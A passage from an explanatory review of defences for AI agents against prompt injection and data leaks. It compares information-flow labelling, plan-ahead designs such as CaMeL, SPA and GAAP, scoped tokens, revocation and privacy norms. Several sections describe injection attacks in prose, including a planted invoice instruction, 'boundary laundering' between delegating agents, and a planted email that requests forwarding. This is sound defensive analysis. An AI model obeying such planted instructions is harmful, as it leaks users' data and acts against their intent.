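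With checks off, ELBA resisted between 425 and 621 of 735 such attacks, depending on the model. With checks on, it resisted all 735, but the share of tasks completed fell from 67–76% to 40–48%. The experiment gives little evidence of how often real attacks succeed, but it is a good test of the checks because they are supposed to work even if an attacker controls the model.

Kravchenko and colleagues tested APPA on Bench-Corp, a set of 20 office tasks they wrote in which restrictions build up and the agent has to keep working. They chose these longer tasks over AgentDojo partly because models now resist AgentDojo's attacks and partly because its tasks end once the agent reaches a single goal. With GPT-5.6 Luna, DeepSeek V4 Flash and Gemini 3.7 Flash, APPA completed 88% to 90% of runs, depending on the model, and no attack succeeded in the 600 protected runs. Unprotected versions completed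 90% to 92.5%, and attacks succeeded in 30% to 39.5% of their runs.

On these tasks, protection lowered the completion rate by only a few points. But when Kravchenko and colleagues removed the branches from the Luna agent, it completed only 56.5% of them. When they instead removed the suggestions that APPA gives an agent after a blocked call, it completed 35%. In both cases it still resisted every attack.

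However, Kravchenko and colleagues designed the tasks, the policies and the system, so the results may not carry over to a firm's own work. On AgentThreatBench, which other developers wrote, APPA completed 64% to 77% of tasks, and again no attacks succeeded. APPA also did much better than FIDES on Bench-Corp, but this is weak evidence about FIDES because Kravchenko and colleagues wrote the FIDES policies themselves, and these couldn't express several of the rules that Bench-Corp tests.

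### Which tasks are still expensive?

Costa and colleagues sorted AgentDojo's tasks by whether the agent can fix its steps in advance.

| Environment | Fixed steps | Fixed steps with a quarantined model | Next step depends on what the agent reads |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 47.5% | 47.5% | 5.0% |
| Travel | 0% | 90.0% | 10.0% |
| Banking | 18.7% | 37.5% | 43.8% |
| Slack | 19.0% | 38.1% | 42.9% |

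Tasks with fixed steps can be protected with almost no loss of usefulness. Kolluri and colleagues also tested Prudentia on WASP, a benchmark in which an agent must post a comment or upvote a post on a web page that contains planted instructions. The steps are the same whatever the page contains. Prudentia needed no approvals and no attack succeeded, while the basic agent was diverted in 15% to 61% of cases, depending on the site and model. Prudentia also completed at least as many tasks as the basic agent, because the planted text never reached its planner.

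Restricting context reduces an agent's usefulness most on tasks where it has to take directions from what it reads. Many of the banking tasks ask the agent to open a file and follow its instructions, for example to schedule a payment. FIDES blocks these payments by design, because the file makes the context untrusted. Better planning can't avoid this, since the user wants the file to determine the payment, so someone has to decide whether to trust the file. The Slack results fit this pattern. Costa and colleagues classify 12 of the 21 Slack tasks as having fixed steps, and ELBA completed 8 to 10 tasks with its checks on.

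AgentDojo's results, though, mostly measure how much usefulness agents lose under restrictions based on trust. They provide much less evidence about restrictions on who may read data. Costa and colleagues hid data in their tests only if it was untrusted. Kolluri and colleagues used the lenient rule described earlier, which lets an agent release restricted data from a trusted context. Bench-Corp does test whether data goes to the right recipients, but only in 20 task designs.

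In principle, the weekly summary should be easy to protect even with strict reader checks, because its steps are fixed. The software could keep all forty messages in variables, and a planner with access to their labels could have the quarantined model summarise only those the manager may read. But if the manager asks whether the project will need a new site engineer in March, the agent may have no useful answer without the colleague's message, which it could use only after an authorised release.

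### Will people read the prompts?

All of these systems need someone to make exceptions, so South's worry about people approving requests by reflex applies here too. Kolluri and colleagues cite research on this "confirmation fatigue", and *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* treats human error as something the design has to allow for. If people stop reading approval prompts, the completion rates that depend on their approvals are misleading.

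This objection is strongest against agents that ask about every action, so it partly supports using labels. In the GPT-5 test, the basic agent needed about three approvals for every four tasks it completed, while Prudentia needed about one for every eleven. People are more likely to read a prompt they see a few times a week than one they see every few minutes.

But nobody read any prompts in that test, because Kolluri and colleagues assumed that users would approve every call in a task that succeeded and stop any call that came from an attack. Real users will sometimes block a legitimate call or approve a malicious one. The saving is also smaller for a firm that uses approvals to catch ordinary mistakes, such as an agent misreading a request. Labels don't catch these mistakes, so the firm will have to keep some prompts that the security policy doesn't need.

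Labels can also make the remaining prompts easier to answer. Kolluri and colleagues suggest showing users the labels and the origin of the data, which an attacker can't alter. Before the agent sends the weekly summary, the software could show the employee the one message that her manager isn't allowed to read. She would then only have to decide whether her manager may know what her colleague told her, instead of searching the whole draft for a sentence that reveals it.

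## Do the restrictions survive memory, delegation and revocation?

If the employee decides that her manager shouldn't know about the resignation, the agent can leave it out of the weekly summary. But the agent may also have saved a note for itself, such as "Bridge: site engineer post opens in March". Suppose the colleague agrees on Wednesday that the employee may tell the manager. Her agent gives the note to a second agent that handles mail, which prepares a message to the manager for Friday morning, but on Thursday the colleague changes his mind.

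The note doesn't name the colleague or quote his message, so its wording doesn't show that it is confidential. The software has to store the message's reader set with the note, along with a link to the original message so that it can find the note if the colleague changes his mind.

A summary can also distort an approval. The colleague agreed that the manager could know, but an agent might shorten this to "he has approved sharing the news". Zhou and Zhang argue that an approval limited to one recipient should keep that limit when an agent summarises it. They suggest linking each claim in a summary to the original evidence and recording which decisions that evidence may influence. Maintaining these links when an agent merges and rewrites several sources is still an open problem.

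### What the agent remembers

Shared memory can leak information without an attacker. *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries*, a position paper by Bhattarai and Vu (2026), gives the example of a research group whose agent saves one scientist's crystallography methods in a shared "playbook". The methods hint at unpublished work. When another user asks what the group is doing, the agent summarises the playbook and reveals that work. The agent saves whatever improves its performance and cannot tell which information is safe to share. Bhattarai and Vu therefore want software outside the model to label stored information and check the labels before the information moves. The audience rule for group chats would provide one such label, since it limits a remembered item to the people present when the agent learned it.

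Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, describe a memory that keeps labels from one request to the next. In their example, an agent retrieves an invoice on Monday that contains an attacker's account number and a planted instruction. On Tuesday, the user asks the agent to pay "the invoice we discussed yesterday". If the agent's planner reads the stored invoice, the instruction can take effect a day late. Even if the planner ignores it, the money may go to the attacker's account. SPA handles the two requests like this:

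1. On Monday, the planner writes a complete plan before any tool runs. The plan includes a description of each expected result, such as "details of the Acme invoice".
2. Ordinary code checks the labels along the whole plan. If the plan passes, the code runs it and stores each result's value, label and description separately.
3. On Tuesday, the planner sees only the descriptions. It chooses the invoice and writes a plan that retrieves it and pays it.
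4. The code looks up Monday's label, finds that the account number is untrusted, and rejects the plan if the payment tool requires trusted input.

The attacker can't tamper with the description, because the planner wrote it before the invoice arrived. SPA also accepts any finite ordering of labels, so a firm could use sets of permitted readers as labels. A plan to send the manager the note about March would then fail the check, no matter how long ago the agent saved the note.

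To test SPA, Girrens and Wang split AgentDojo's 97 tasks into conversations of two to five requests. The planner used GPT-5.4 nano, a small model.

| Version of SPA | Tasks completed without an attack | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| Planner sees stored values, no label checks | 65.9% | 0.6% |
| Planner sees descriptions, no label checks | 62.5% | 0.3% |
| Planner sees descriptions, with label checks | 35.3% | 0.2% |

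Hiding the stored values caused few failures. When an earlier request had saved the necessary result, later plans retrieved it 95.4% of the time without label checks and 89.9% with them. The label checks caused many more failures, stopping about 45% of runs, typically because a plan passed an untrusted result to a tool that required trusted input.

The attack results are weak evidence on whether SPA makes memory safer, so the argument for SPA rests mainly on its design. Attacks rarely worked even when the planner could read stored values, and Girrens and Wang acknowledge that their attack is a weak test of instructions that lie dormant in memory. SPA had also rejected the plan in two of the runs counted as successful attacks with label checks on.

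### Data that leaves and comes back

An agent can also lose track of data by sending it to an outside service and retrieving it later. *An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data* (Stanley, Verma and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that checks its user in for a flight and gives the airline her passport number. She later asks the agent to fetch the confirmation and email it to a friend. The confirmation may contain the passport number, but it comes from the airline as new data.

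GAAP keeps a disclosure log that records each private item the agent has shared, who received it, when, and through which tool call. When the airline returns the confirmation, GAAP labels it as possibly containing anything the airline has received before. GAAP then checks whether the user has allowed her friend to have her passport number. If she hasn't decided, GAAP asks her. Descriptions of each tool can make the labels less cautious, for example by stating that a food-ordering service returns the order but never the password.

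GAAP stores the user's decisions in a separate database as pairs of a data item and a recipient, so it doesn't ask again in later tasks. The user can withdraw a permission at any time or allow a disclosure just once. The log still records a one-time disclosure, since the recipient now has the data.

If the employee's agent saved its note in a file, the log would link the file to the colleague's message. GAAP could then prompt the employee about the message before another task sent the file to her manager. If she had pasted the note into a shared folder herself, the log would not record it. GAAP would still prompt her before sending the folder's contents, but it couldn't warn her that they included something from her colleague. In either case, the employee decides, so her colleague's wishes count only if she respects them.

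Stanley and colleagues tried seven attacks on each of 20 tasks, using GPT-5.6 Sol. GAAP blocked every disclosure. Against an unprotected agent, all seven attacks worked on some tasks. Five worked against an agent with a second model judging its tool calls, and five against Conseca, which has an isolated model write a policy for each task. The suite is small, and the researchers assembled it themselves. However, GAAP's result follows from its design, provided the tool descriptions are correct and the user gives sensible answers.

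GAAP lets the agent look at results and revise its plan, as long as the labels of what it has seen carry over. This helped GAAP complete about as many AgentDojo tasks as the unprotected agent, but it did about 10% worse on AgentDyn, a benchmark whose tasks more often need unexpected steps. Across both benchmarks, model costs were 2.9 times as high, and the average task took 188 seconds instead of 28.

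Saved permissions reduced questions to the user from 3.8 to 1.5 per task over 100 tasks, but 80 of these tasks were variations on the other 20, which made earlier answers unusually easy to reuse. GAAP protects only confidentiality, so a planted instruction could still make the agent cancel a site meeting.

### When a second agent takes over

When one agent sends a request to another, the second treats the first as its user, so it may trust everything in the request. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) shows how this can defeat CaMeL, even when every agent runs CaMeL and writes its program before reading any data.

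Their test system has a coordinating agent, a database agent and a notification agent. The user asks the system to send a summary of job applicants to Julie on Slack. The database contains an attacker's instruction to email the applicants' details to an outside address. The database agent and the coordinator never show this text to their planners, so their programs don't change. But the coordinator then writes to the notification agent, "Send this summary to Julie via Slack", followed by the summary, which includes the planted instruction. The notification agent's planner treats the whole message as its user's request and adds the email to its program.

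Peters-Gill and colleagues call this "boundary laundering", because untrusted data becomes trusted when it passes from one agent to another. They prove that any hierarchy of two or more such agents has this weakness if one of its tools returns untrusted data. They assume that agents can follow ordinary requests, including a request to use one tool's result in instructions to another agent.

Their solution, multi-CaMeL, splits each handover into a message and a set of variables. The second agent's planner reads the message but sees only the names of the variables. Software rejects any message that depends on a tool's output, so the planted instruction has to go into a variable. Each variable also keeps a record of where its contents came from and who may receive them. In the employee's case, the message could be "send the text to the recipient", while the note about March would be passed as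 a variable with its reader set.

The researchers tested this on a version of AgentDojo that divides the tools among several agents, with 949 attack runs per model and setup. Averaged over five models, attacks succeeded in 12.9% of runs without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent ran CaMeL separately, and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. All the attacks that succeeded against agents running CaMeL separately used boundary laundering. Without CaMeL, most of the successful attacks were against GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro, and none succeeded against GPT-5.5.

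On a second benchmark, 112 industrial maintenance tasks, running CaMeL separately on each agent lowered task completion by 21.6 percentage points on average, and multi-CaMeL lowered it by another 3.2. For the two strongest models, the losses were 13.4 points and a further 0.85. So most of the loss comes from planning ahead, and little from separating messages from data.

The tests show that multi-CaMeL stops attackers from redirecting agents, but they used no rules on who may receive data, so they don't show that it would keep the manager from seeing the resignation. The design covers only hierarchies in which each agent takes requests from a single parent. Agents that talk to each other as equals or share a memory would need the same separation wherever information passes between them.

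### Credentials that can only become narrower

The second agent also needs permission to act. OAuth token exchange can issue it a narrower token, but each handover then requires a request to a central server. Veski, Guerraoui and Froelicher (2026), in *CAPMAS*, instead use Macaroons, tokens that an agent can restrict without contacting the server. Each restriction adds a step to a chain of signatures:

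s₀ = HMAC(secret, "rid=123")
s₁ = HMAC(s₀, "domain=projects")
s₂ = HMAC(s₁, "op=read")

Here `rid` is the number of the user's request, and HMAC is a function that is easy to compute but practically impossible to reverse. An agent that holds s₁ can add "op=read" and pass on s₂. The next agent can add more restrictions, but it can't remove "op=read", because that would require s₁, which it can't recover from s₂. The central server knows the secret, so it can recompute the chain from the listed restrictions and check the final signature.

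CAPMAS sets the initial limits by comparing the user's request with descriptions of all available permissions and choosing the closest matches. This found the complete set of permissions for about 90% of test requests in under 20 milliseconds. Narrowing a token was 30 times faster than token exchange, and the system made about half as many network calls. Veski and colleagues assume that the software around each model passes tokens on honestly. The signatures prevent an agent from removing restrictions, but the agent still has to choose to narrow its token.

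The signatures can't protect a restriction that never made it into the token. This is what went wrong in Zhou and Zhang's earlier example, where permission to send summary S to Alice became a token that means "send mail". They express the missing requirement as

α(E(M(P))) ⊆ ⟦P⟧.

P is the approved policy, and M(P) is the set of credentials and checks that implement it. E(M(P)) contains the effects those controls allow, such as a particular message reaching a particular address. The function α translates these effects into the policy's terms, and ⟦P⟧ contains everything the policy permits. The condition is that the implementation must not allow anything the policy forbids. Here the policy permits only "S goes to Alice", but the token also allows "S goes to Bob", so the condition fails even though the token is valid. Putting the recipient and content limits in the token could fix this, as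 could enforcing them before the request reaches the mail service.

Checking this condition requires knowing what each tool can do. Zhou and Zhang propose "effect contracts", which list the data a tool can access or send, its possible recipients and the changes it can make. A contract for the Slack server described earlier would have to include the fact that posting a link can cause Slack to contact an outside address. If a tool starts forwarding data to a new company, its contract has to change even if the tool's name and inputs stay the same. Software can check the condition automatically, but only if the policies and contracts use a sufficiently simple formal language and the tools can't bypass the controls.

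### Two agents, one purchase

A credential can be correct and still allow too much when several agents share a limit. Zhou and Zhang describe an agent that may buy one item and delegates the purchase to two others, allowing each to buy one. Each delegate stays within its own limit, but together they can buy two items. Macaroons don't solve this, because the agent could give both delegates a token marked "one purchase".

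The agents need a shared record of what they have used. Before an agent buys an item, the system has to check the remaining allowance and record the reservation in one indivisible step, so that two agents can't both claim the last item. The calendar limit discussed earlier would need the same kind of record if two agents could disclose free times.

Retries can also exceed a limit. If a shop doesn't answer in time, the agent may try again even though the first order went through. Conventional software gives both attempts the same identifier so that the shop can recognise a duplicate. An agent may instead change its plan after the delay, for example by splitting the order or using another shop, so that the second attempt no longer matches the first. Until the agent learns whether the first order went through, the system has to keep the item reserved. This can block useful work, but releasing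 the reservation could lead to a second purchase.

### Taking permission back

If the employee withdraws her agent's right to use the mail agent, the system has to work out which other agents lose their authority. If an accounts agent also uses the mail agent, cutting off the mail agent completely would disrupt the accounts work. But if the mail agent had passed part of the employee's task to a translation agent at another company, a system that searched only the firm's own records would miss the translation agent.

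Liu, Yu and Jiang (2026), in *VERA*, represent delegations as arrows in a graph G that starts from trusted sources of authority. If someone withdraws delegation e, the agents that should lose their authority are

T(e, G) = reach(G) \ reach(G \ {e}),

where reach(G) contains every agent that can trace its authority back to a trusted source. In words, an agent loses its authority only if every such path used e. The mail agent therefore keeps working for accounts, while the translation agent loses its authority if it depended entirely on the employee's delegation.

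The system has to process simultaneous withdrawals together. Suppose the employee's agent and the accounts agent both withdraw their delegations. Each withdrawal on its own leaves the mail agent with one remaining path, so a system that calculates them separately and combines the results would leave the mail agent active, although it no longer has any authority.

Liu and colleagues ran 25 combinations of workflows and inputs 20 times each. Thirteen of the combinations included agents with more than one source of authority. In 320 cases, VERA correctly preserved a shared agent that a simpler method, which cuts off everything below a withdrawn delegation, would have removed. VERA doesn't deliver withdrawal notices, so an agent that hasn't received one may keep working. VERA's formula also assumes that one valid path is enough, so a firm that requires two approvals would need a different rule.

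VERA determines who may act, but it doesn't remove information. If the mail agent keeps working for accounts, it may still have the note about March. Zhou and Zhang explain that the effect of a withdrawal depends on how far an operation has gone. For the colleague's change of mind on Thursday, this means:

| Where the information is | What the firm can still do |
|---|---|
| In the original message | Block future reads |
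| In a note or another agent's memory | Block further use and sharing, if the copy has a link to its source |
| In a message that the agent hasn't submitted | Stop it, if the agent checks permissions again before sending |
| In a message that the mail service has accepted | Cancel it, if the service allows this |
| In the manager's inbox after delivery | Ask the manager to delete it, but not make her forget it |

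The agent therefore has to store the unsent message with its reader set and a reference to the permission that allowed it, then check on Friday whether that permission is still valid. SPA's stored labels would not be enough, because SPA restores the label from the day it saved the note. If that label included the manager, someone would have to update it after the colleague changed his mind. GAAP looks up permissions before each tool call, so if the employee withdraws the permission on Thursday, it will block a call to send the message on Friday.

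But if the mail agent gave the message to the mail service on Wednesday for delivery on Friday, GAAP has already approved the call. Revoking the agent's token won't cancel the message, so the firm has to ask the mail service to stop it. If the service doesn't respond, the agent should record that the manager may already know.

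## How should an information boundary be defined, and who sets it?

Stopping Friday's message helps only if the rule that blocks it is right. Labels, tokens and disclosure logs can enforce a decision about who may learn what, but someone has to make that decision first, and they can express it in several ways.

Suppose the employee's private calendar has an entry for Thursday at 10, "oncology consultation". Her manager has called a meeting for the same hour, and she tells her agent, "Move Thursday's meeting with my manager." The agent could write any of these messages:

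1. To the manager: "Could we meet on Friday at 10 instead?"
2. To the manager: "She has an oncology consultation on Thursday. Could we meet on Friday at 10 instead?"
3. To the hospital: "Could she come to the oncology clinic on Friday instead?"

The firm could define the boundary by the resources the agent may use, the task, the people who may read the data, or the norms of the setting, meaning what people there expect to happen to information. Which of the four it chooses affects what information the agent may use or share.

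| Boundary | New time to the manager | New time and reason to the manager | Request to the hospital |
|---|---|---|---|
| Resources | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |
| Task | Allowed | Allowed | Blocked |
| Permitted readers | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked |
| Norms of the setting | Allowed | Blocked | Allowed |

If the agent may read the calendar and send mail, a boundary around resources allows all three messages. A grant for this task lets the agent read her calendar and send her manager one message. That rules out moving the hospital appointment, but it allows either the first message or the second.

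Only the employee may read her calendar, which also shows her free hour on Friday. Under a strict rule on readers, the software would have to block all three messages or ask her about each one. It would even block the message to the hospital, which made the appointment, unless someone had listed the hospital as a reader.

Under ordinary workplace norms, a manager may learn when the employee is free but not which clinic she attends. The hospital already has the appointment in its records, so the third message tells it almost nothing new. But the agent would still be moving the wrong event, and norms about information don't prevent that.

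### Contextual integrity

The last row of the table follows contextual integrity, a theory Helen Nissenbaum published in 2004. It defines privacy as information flowing in ways that fit the norms of the setting, rather than as secrecy. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (2026) lists the five parameters that describe each flow. In the second message, the data subject is the employee, the sender is her agent, the recipient is her manager, and the type of information is medical. The fifth parameter, the transmission principle, is the condition that makes a flow acceptable, such as the employee's consent, a legal duty or a professional role, and the second message meets no such condition.

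A flow respects contextual integrity only if all five parameters fit the norms, according to *Privacy Conductor* (2026), so changing one can change whether the flow is acceptable. For example, the second message would be fine if the employee had asked the agent to explain her absence. *Do LLMs Know What Is Private Internally?* (2026) builds test cases by varying one parameter. In one, a coworker knows about Jordan's chronic illness and has Jordan's explicit permission to share it. Only the person asking changes, and may be a specialist, a relative, an employer, a stranger or a journalist. The permission doesn't settle all five cases, since Jordan may have meant it only for the specialist.

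The theory needs a source of norms. *Privacy Conductor* recounts how Barth and colleagues took norms from legislation and wrote them in a formal logic that can express the order of events, while later researchers asked people to judge short scenarios. A survey can show what most people find acceptable, but this employee's case may differ. She may have told her manager about her illness months ago, or she may want nobody at work to know that she ever visits a hospital. Norms also differ between places. *Security and Privacy in Agentic AI* (Jenkins, Kitkowska and colleagues, 2026), which reports on a workshop of thirty experts, warns that an agent may work across countries and organisations with conflicting assumptions about autonomy and acceptable risk.

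Norms therefore produce the most sensible results for the manager, but they are the hardest of the four boundaries to implement in software. Boundaries based on resources, tasks or readers are easier to check, and a useful definition can include parts of them.

### A working definition

An information boundary can be written as a rule that lets information from a named source reach a named recipient, for a stated purpose, after a permitted transformation and until a stated time. For the employee's meeting, it could look like this:

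| Element | Rule for this meeting | What it prevents |
|---|---|---|
| Source | Her calendar for Thursday and Friday | Use of other data the agent happens to see |
| Recipient | Her manager | Disclosure to other people or outside services |
| Purpose | Moving this meeting | Use of her free times for something else |
| Permitted transformation | Reduce entries to free and busy times | Disclosure of the reason |
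| Duration | Until the meeting has a new time | Later use of a saved copy |

Naming the source matters because an agent often sees more than it needs. *Capable but Careless* (2026) tests agents that operate a computer through its screen. In some scenarios, prohibited items such as neighbouring calendar entries appear next to the one the agent needs. In others, the user makes a vague request like "summarise my list", or the same content suits one recipient but not another. The source element should also record whom the data is about. Otherwise, the rule no longer accounts for the colleague who plans to resign once his message reaches the employee's mailbox.

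The recipient element has to cover software as well as people. *The Claws in Plain Sight* (2026) examines agents that pass private context to third-party add-ons through tool-call inputs. The paper also shows why purpose needs its own element. Its example is a postal address, which is appropriate to share for arranging a delivery but not for a product-support request. The same company could receive the address in both cases, so a list of permitted recipients wouldn't separate the two uses.

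*Say Something Else* (2026) bases the permitted transformation on how much information is enough for the recipient. An agent can suppress a detail by leaving it out, or generalise it, for example by writing "appointment" instead of "oncology consultation". The manager needs only a new time for this meeting. For a six-week absence, the manager would need to know more, and the personnel department might need a medical certificate.

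Software can enforce some of these elements better than others. It can check a recipient or an expiry time exactly, reduce a calendar to free and busy times, and track the source with labels. Purpose is the hardest to enforce. Software can tie a rule to one approved task, as mission-bound OAuth does, but it can't stop the manager from using the answer for something else afterwards.

The records that support these checks are sensitive too. A log that links Friday's meeting to an oncology consultation contains medical information, even if the message to the manager doesn't. Jenkins and colleagues call this a paradox of traceability, because investigators need detailed logs to work out what an agent did, but the logs can become a form of surveillance. Their suggestions include limiting access to incident records by role and keeping routine data for less time than evidence that regulators need.

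### Alice, Bob and the difference between evidence and authority

A rule may leave a detail for the agent to find out. In an example from Zhou and Zhang, a user lets an agent send a report to the approved contact at a partner firm, and a trusted directory lists Alice as that contact. The agent then reads a document containing an instruction to copy in Bob. Following that instruction would change the user's rule, whereas the directory only supplies the detail the rule left open.

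Bob may really be the partner's new finance director and have a good reason to want the report, but the user hasn't given whoever wrote the document the authority to add recipients. The agent can pass the request on to someone who has that authority.

Evidence also has to be reliable for the question it is used to answer. If an attacker replaces Alice's address in the directory, the report goes to the attacker even though the rule hasn't changed. The firm therefore has to protect the directory as well as the permissions.

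This distinction is still necessary when the format of an answer is limited. Zhou and Zhang describe a workflow that asks a source whether a draft is approved for external release and accepts only "yes" or "no". A "yes" can release the whole draft, so the system has to check that the answer comes from someone entitled to approve the release.

A user can also give a source limited authority in advance. For example, the employee might let her agent follow instructions in her manager's task list that only involve booking rooms or preparing agendas. An instruction in the list to send out personnel files would still need separate approval.

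*AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* treats prompt injection as a violation of contextual integrity's norms, which can govern actions as well as data. Under such norms, a subcontractor may email the agent to say when the concrete will arrive, but not to tell it where to send the bid prices.

### Who writes the rules?

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* expects an authorised user, an administrator or an application developer to set the policy. It also warns that correct enforcement doesn't prove that the policy matches what people intended.

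A firm can start with the file permissions and sensitivity labels it already has. This saves work, but the agent inherits every mistake in them. The Ontario hospital's invitation list, for instance, still included a physician who had left the year before. A label such as "confidential" may also not specify who can see the file or for what purpose. Overlapping permissions can make access hard to remove. Sharma and Grossman note that in AC4A, deleting a permission for part of a calendar may leave access in place if another permission covers the same part. They leave it to the user to manage such overlaps.

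A single policy written by an administrator or developer won't suit everyone, because people differ in what they want an agent to share. *How Agents Ask for Permission* (Michael and Roesner, 2026) gives the example of a rule that lets an agent send passport details only to recognised airlines. The rule would frustrate a customer of a specialist travel agency, and it would be too loose for someone who never wants an agent to share their passport number.

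#### Rules that users write

Users could set the boundary by writing their own rules. Yan (2026) tested this approach in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* with 113 people who had no professional software background. Each supervised a simulated day in which an agent attempted 18 actions, including 7 that went beyond the user's requests. One group approved or refused every action, another relied on a model to review them, and a third set rules in advance. The third group chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories: spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting something, and accessing private information.

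The people who wrote rules got the least protection. They blocked 20.1 percentage points less of the overreach than the group that reviewed every action (95% confidence interval 8.1 to 32.1), and 14.5 points less than the automated review (3.2 to 25.8). They had chosen "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, so they still had to make most decisions when prompted. Of the 148 unrequested actions that went ahead in this group, they had approved 133 at the prompt.

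Yan compared whole designs, so the study doesn't explain why people approved more after writing rules. Some participants may also have wanted the extra actions, since "overreach" here means anything outside the original request. But the result is evidence against the idea that people will settle difficult cases in advance if given a simple form. Participants mostly postponed the decision, and the rules reduced the average number of prompts only from 18.0 to 10.9.

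People also don't reliably limit an agent to the data it needs. In *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, Wu, Yang and colleagues (2025) asked 205 people to train an imaginary assistant and make 20 decisions each about sharing data. A quarter of the requests included data that the task didn't need. No participant gave suitable permissions every time. Participants shared unnecessary data about 78% of the time when they mistakenly thought the task needed it, and about 38% of the time even when they recognised that it didn't.

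Wu and colleagues then built a model to predict these decisions from each person's earlier choices and the choices of similar people. It was 85.1% accurate overall and 94.4% accurate on its most confident predictions. Accuracy was 66.9% without any history for the person, and including decisions from one to four earlier queries raised it by 10.8%.

Such a model could save people many prompts, but its predictions were counted as "right" when they matched what the person chose, so if people tend to share too much, a perfect predictor will too. Broad categories won't be enough either, because preferences varied within them. For travel tasks, participants chose "always share" for 43.9% of requests involving a calendar but only 17.8% of those involving cloud storage, which held passport scans and visa records.

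#### Rules that a model writes

Tsai and Bagdasarian (2025), in *Contextual Agent Security*, propose Conseca, in which a language model writes a new policy for each task:

1. The policy model receives the user's request, the tool descriptions and some context that the developer trusts, such as names and email addresses. It doesn't receive the text of any emails.
2. It writes limits for each tool and a plain-language reason for each limit. The developer can have the user approve them.
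3. The agent works on the task and reads whatever it needs.
4. Before each action, ordinary code checks the limits. If an action breaks them, the agent gets the reason and can try something else.

In one example, Alice asks the agent to answer urgent work emails. The policy allows it to send mail from Alice to work.com addresses if the subject line contains "urgent", and forbids it to delete anything. A planted instruction can't change this policy, because the policy model never receives it.

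Tsai and Bagdasarian tested a Conseca prototype on 20 office tasks. On average, the agent completed 14.0 tasks without a policy, 12.0 with Conseca, 12.2 with a fixed policy that allowed everything except deletion, and none with a fixed policy that forbade all changes. They also planted an email asking for messages about security vulnerabilities to be forwarded. Conseca blocked the forwarding in every task except the one in which the user had asked the agent to carry out the tasks in urgent emails. The results show that the idea can work, but the researchers wrote the tasks themselves and planted only one email.

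The Conseca paper acknowledges that the policy is only as good as the model's grasp of the user's preferences and social norms. The model also can't foresee actions that depend on text it isn't allowed to read, such as tasks in a manager's email. In the paper's own example, the stated reason limits recipients to a list of known work users, but the actual limit accepts any address at work.com. Conseca relies on experts to catch such mismatches.

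*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that Conseca's guarantees assume the policy model is safe, and that a hijacked agent could predict the policy and choose steps that each look harmless but together cause damage. Conseca checks each action separately, and Tsai and Bagdasarian leave limits on sequences of actions to future work. For the employee's meeting, a Conseca policy could allow the message to be sent only to her manager's address. But the prototype checks inputs by matching text patterns, and it would be hard to write a pattern that catches every way of revealing an illness.

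#### What current systems offer

Michael and Roesner reviewed 21 systems, published between 2024 and 2026, that support different permissions for different users. Twelve try to reduce the user's work, eleven base their rules on formal methods, and twelve make enforcement predictable, either with ordinary code or by asking the user. None fully does all three. Only six clearly let users change or withdraw permissions later, and two of those allow it only between sessions.

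They also tried five commercial agents in May and June 2026. These usually either asked for approval very often or let a model decide with little explanation. Claude's chatbot had a "Needs approval" setting but sometimes approved actions itself, such as creating an email draft. In chat mode, ChatGPT asked about every action covered by a permission. Its agent mode, which controls a remote browser, had no permission settings for that browser. Codex had an automatic reviewer that users could turn off only for all tools at once. The companies may have changed these products since.

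A workable arrangement would let the employer set outer limits, the employee tighten them, and a model suggest narrower rules for each task. When rules conflict, the strictest could apply, as it does in the software Yan built. Loosening a limit would then need approval from someone with authority over it. The colleague would still have no say unless the system gave him one, for example by letting him register his message as FlowSeal does.

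### When a conclusion is more sensitive than the facts

Even a carefully written rule about sources can miss what an agent works out from them. Suppose the construction firm has 60 employees, and every manager may read three documents:

- A personnel notice says that one employee, whom it doesn't name, is having cancer treatment and asks managers to be flexible about hours.
- The shared calendar shows that six employees are away every third Tuesday.
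- The site rota shows that five employees are excused from dusty work.

From the notice alone, each employee has a 1 in 60 chance of being the patient. If the treatment explains the Tuesday absences, the chance rises to 1 in 6 for each person in the calendar group. If it also explains the excuse from dusty work, the patient is the only person in both the calendar group and the rota group.

The labels don't prevent this. If M is the set of managers, each document has the reader set M, and the conclusion gets

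M ∩ M ∩ M = M.

The software therefore lets the agent tell any manager which person has cancer. That conclusion should have fewer permitted readers than any of the three documents, but combining the documents' labels only preserves their existing restrictions and can't add a new one.

*Agents That Know Too Much* (2026), a survey of privacy in agents, distinguishes two versions of the problem. In inference, a single response lets someone deduce a fact they haven't seen. In composition, the fact emerges only when someone combines two or more responses. For example, the manager could ask one agent who is away on Tuesdays and another who is excused from dusty work, then compare the answers herself. According to the survey, checks on individual steps are least effective against composition.

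The agent may also reveal a conclusion without stating it. *InferPriv* (2026) studies whether assistants leave cues in everyday messages that let a recipient infer something sensitive about the user. It notes that earlier privacy tests looked only for direct disclosure. The message "Please don't give her Tuesday shifts until the treatment ends" doesn't name an illness, but a manager who has read the notice will understand what it refers to.

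The problem also affects data without names. TechRadar's *AI agents are about to make access control obsolete* describes a retailer's assistant that has no access to personal details but uses activity logs, support tickets and purchases to list the customers most likely to cancel. The example is hypothetical and comes from the co-founder of a security company, so it illustrates the problem but doesn't show how common it is.

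#### Partial remedies

The firm can keep the facts apart by giving an agent only the sources its task needs. An agent that plans shifts needs the rota and the calendar but not the personnel notice, and without the notice it has much less reason to suspect cancer. This is the most dependable remedy because it works before the agent starts reasoning, but it fails when a task needs all the sources or when people combine the answers afterwards.

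Another option is to restrict particular combinations. The firm could decide that only the personnel department may read anything based on both the notice and the attendance records. Software can enforce this with labels that record sources, but somebody has to think of the combination first. With n sources, there are 2ⁿ − n − 1 combinations of two or more, which is 4 for three documents and about 1.1 trillion for forty emails. A firm can therefore list only the dangerous combinations it already knows about.

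The firm could instead restrict the conclusion, for example by forbidding agents to tell managers about any named employee's health, whatever the source. This restriction corresponds to the type of information in contextual integrity, and it would also cover the cancer example without a list of combinations. But a model would have to judge whether each message reveals someone's health, and it could easily miss the sentence about Tuesday shifts.

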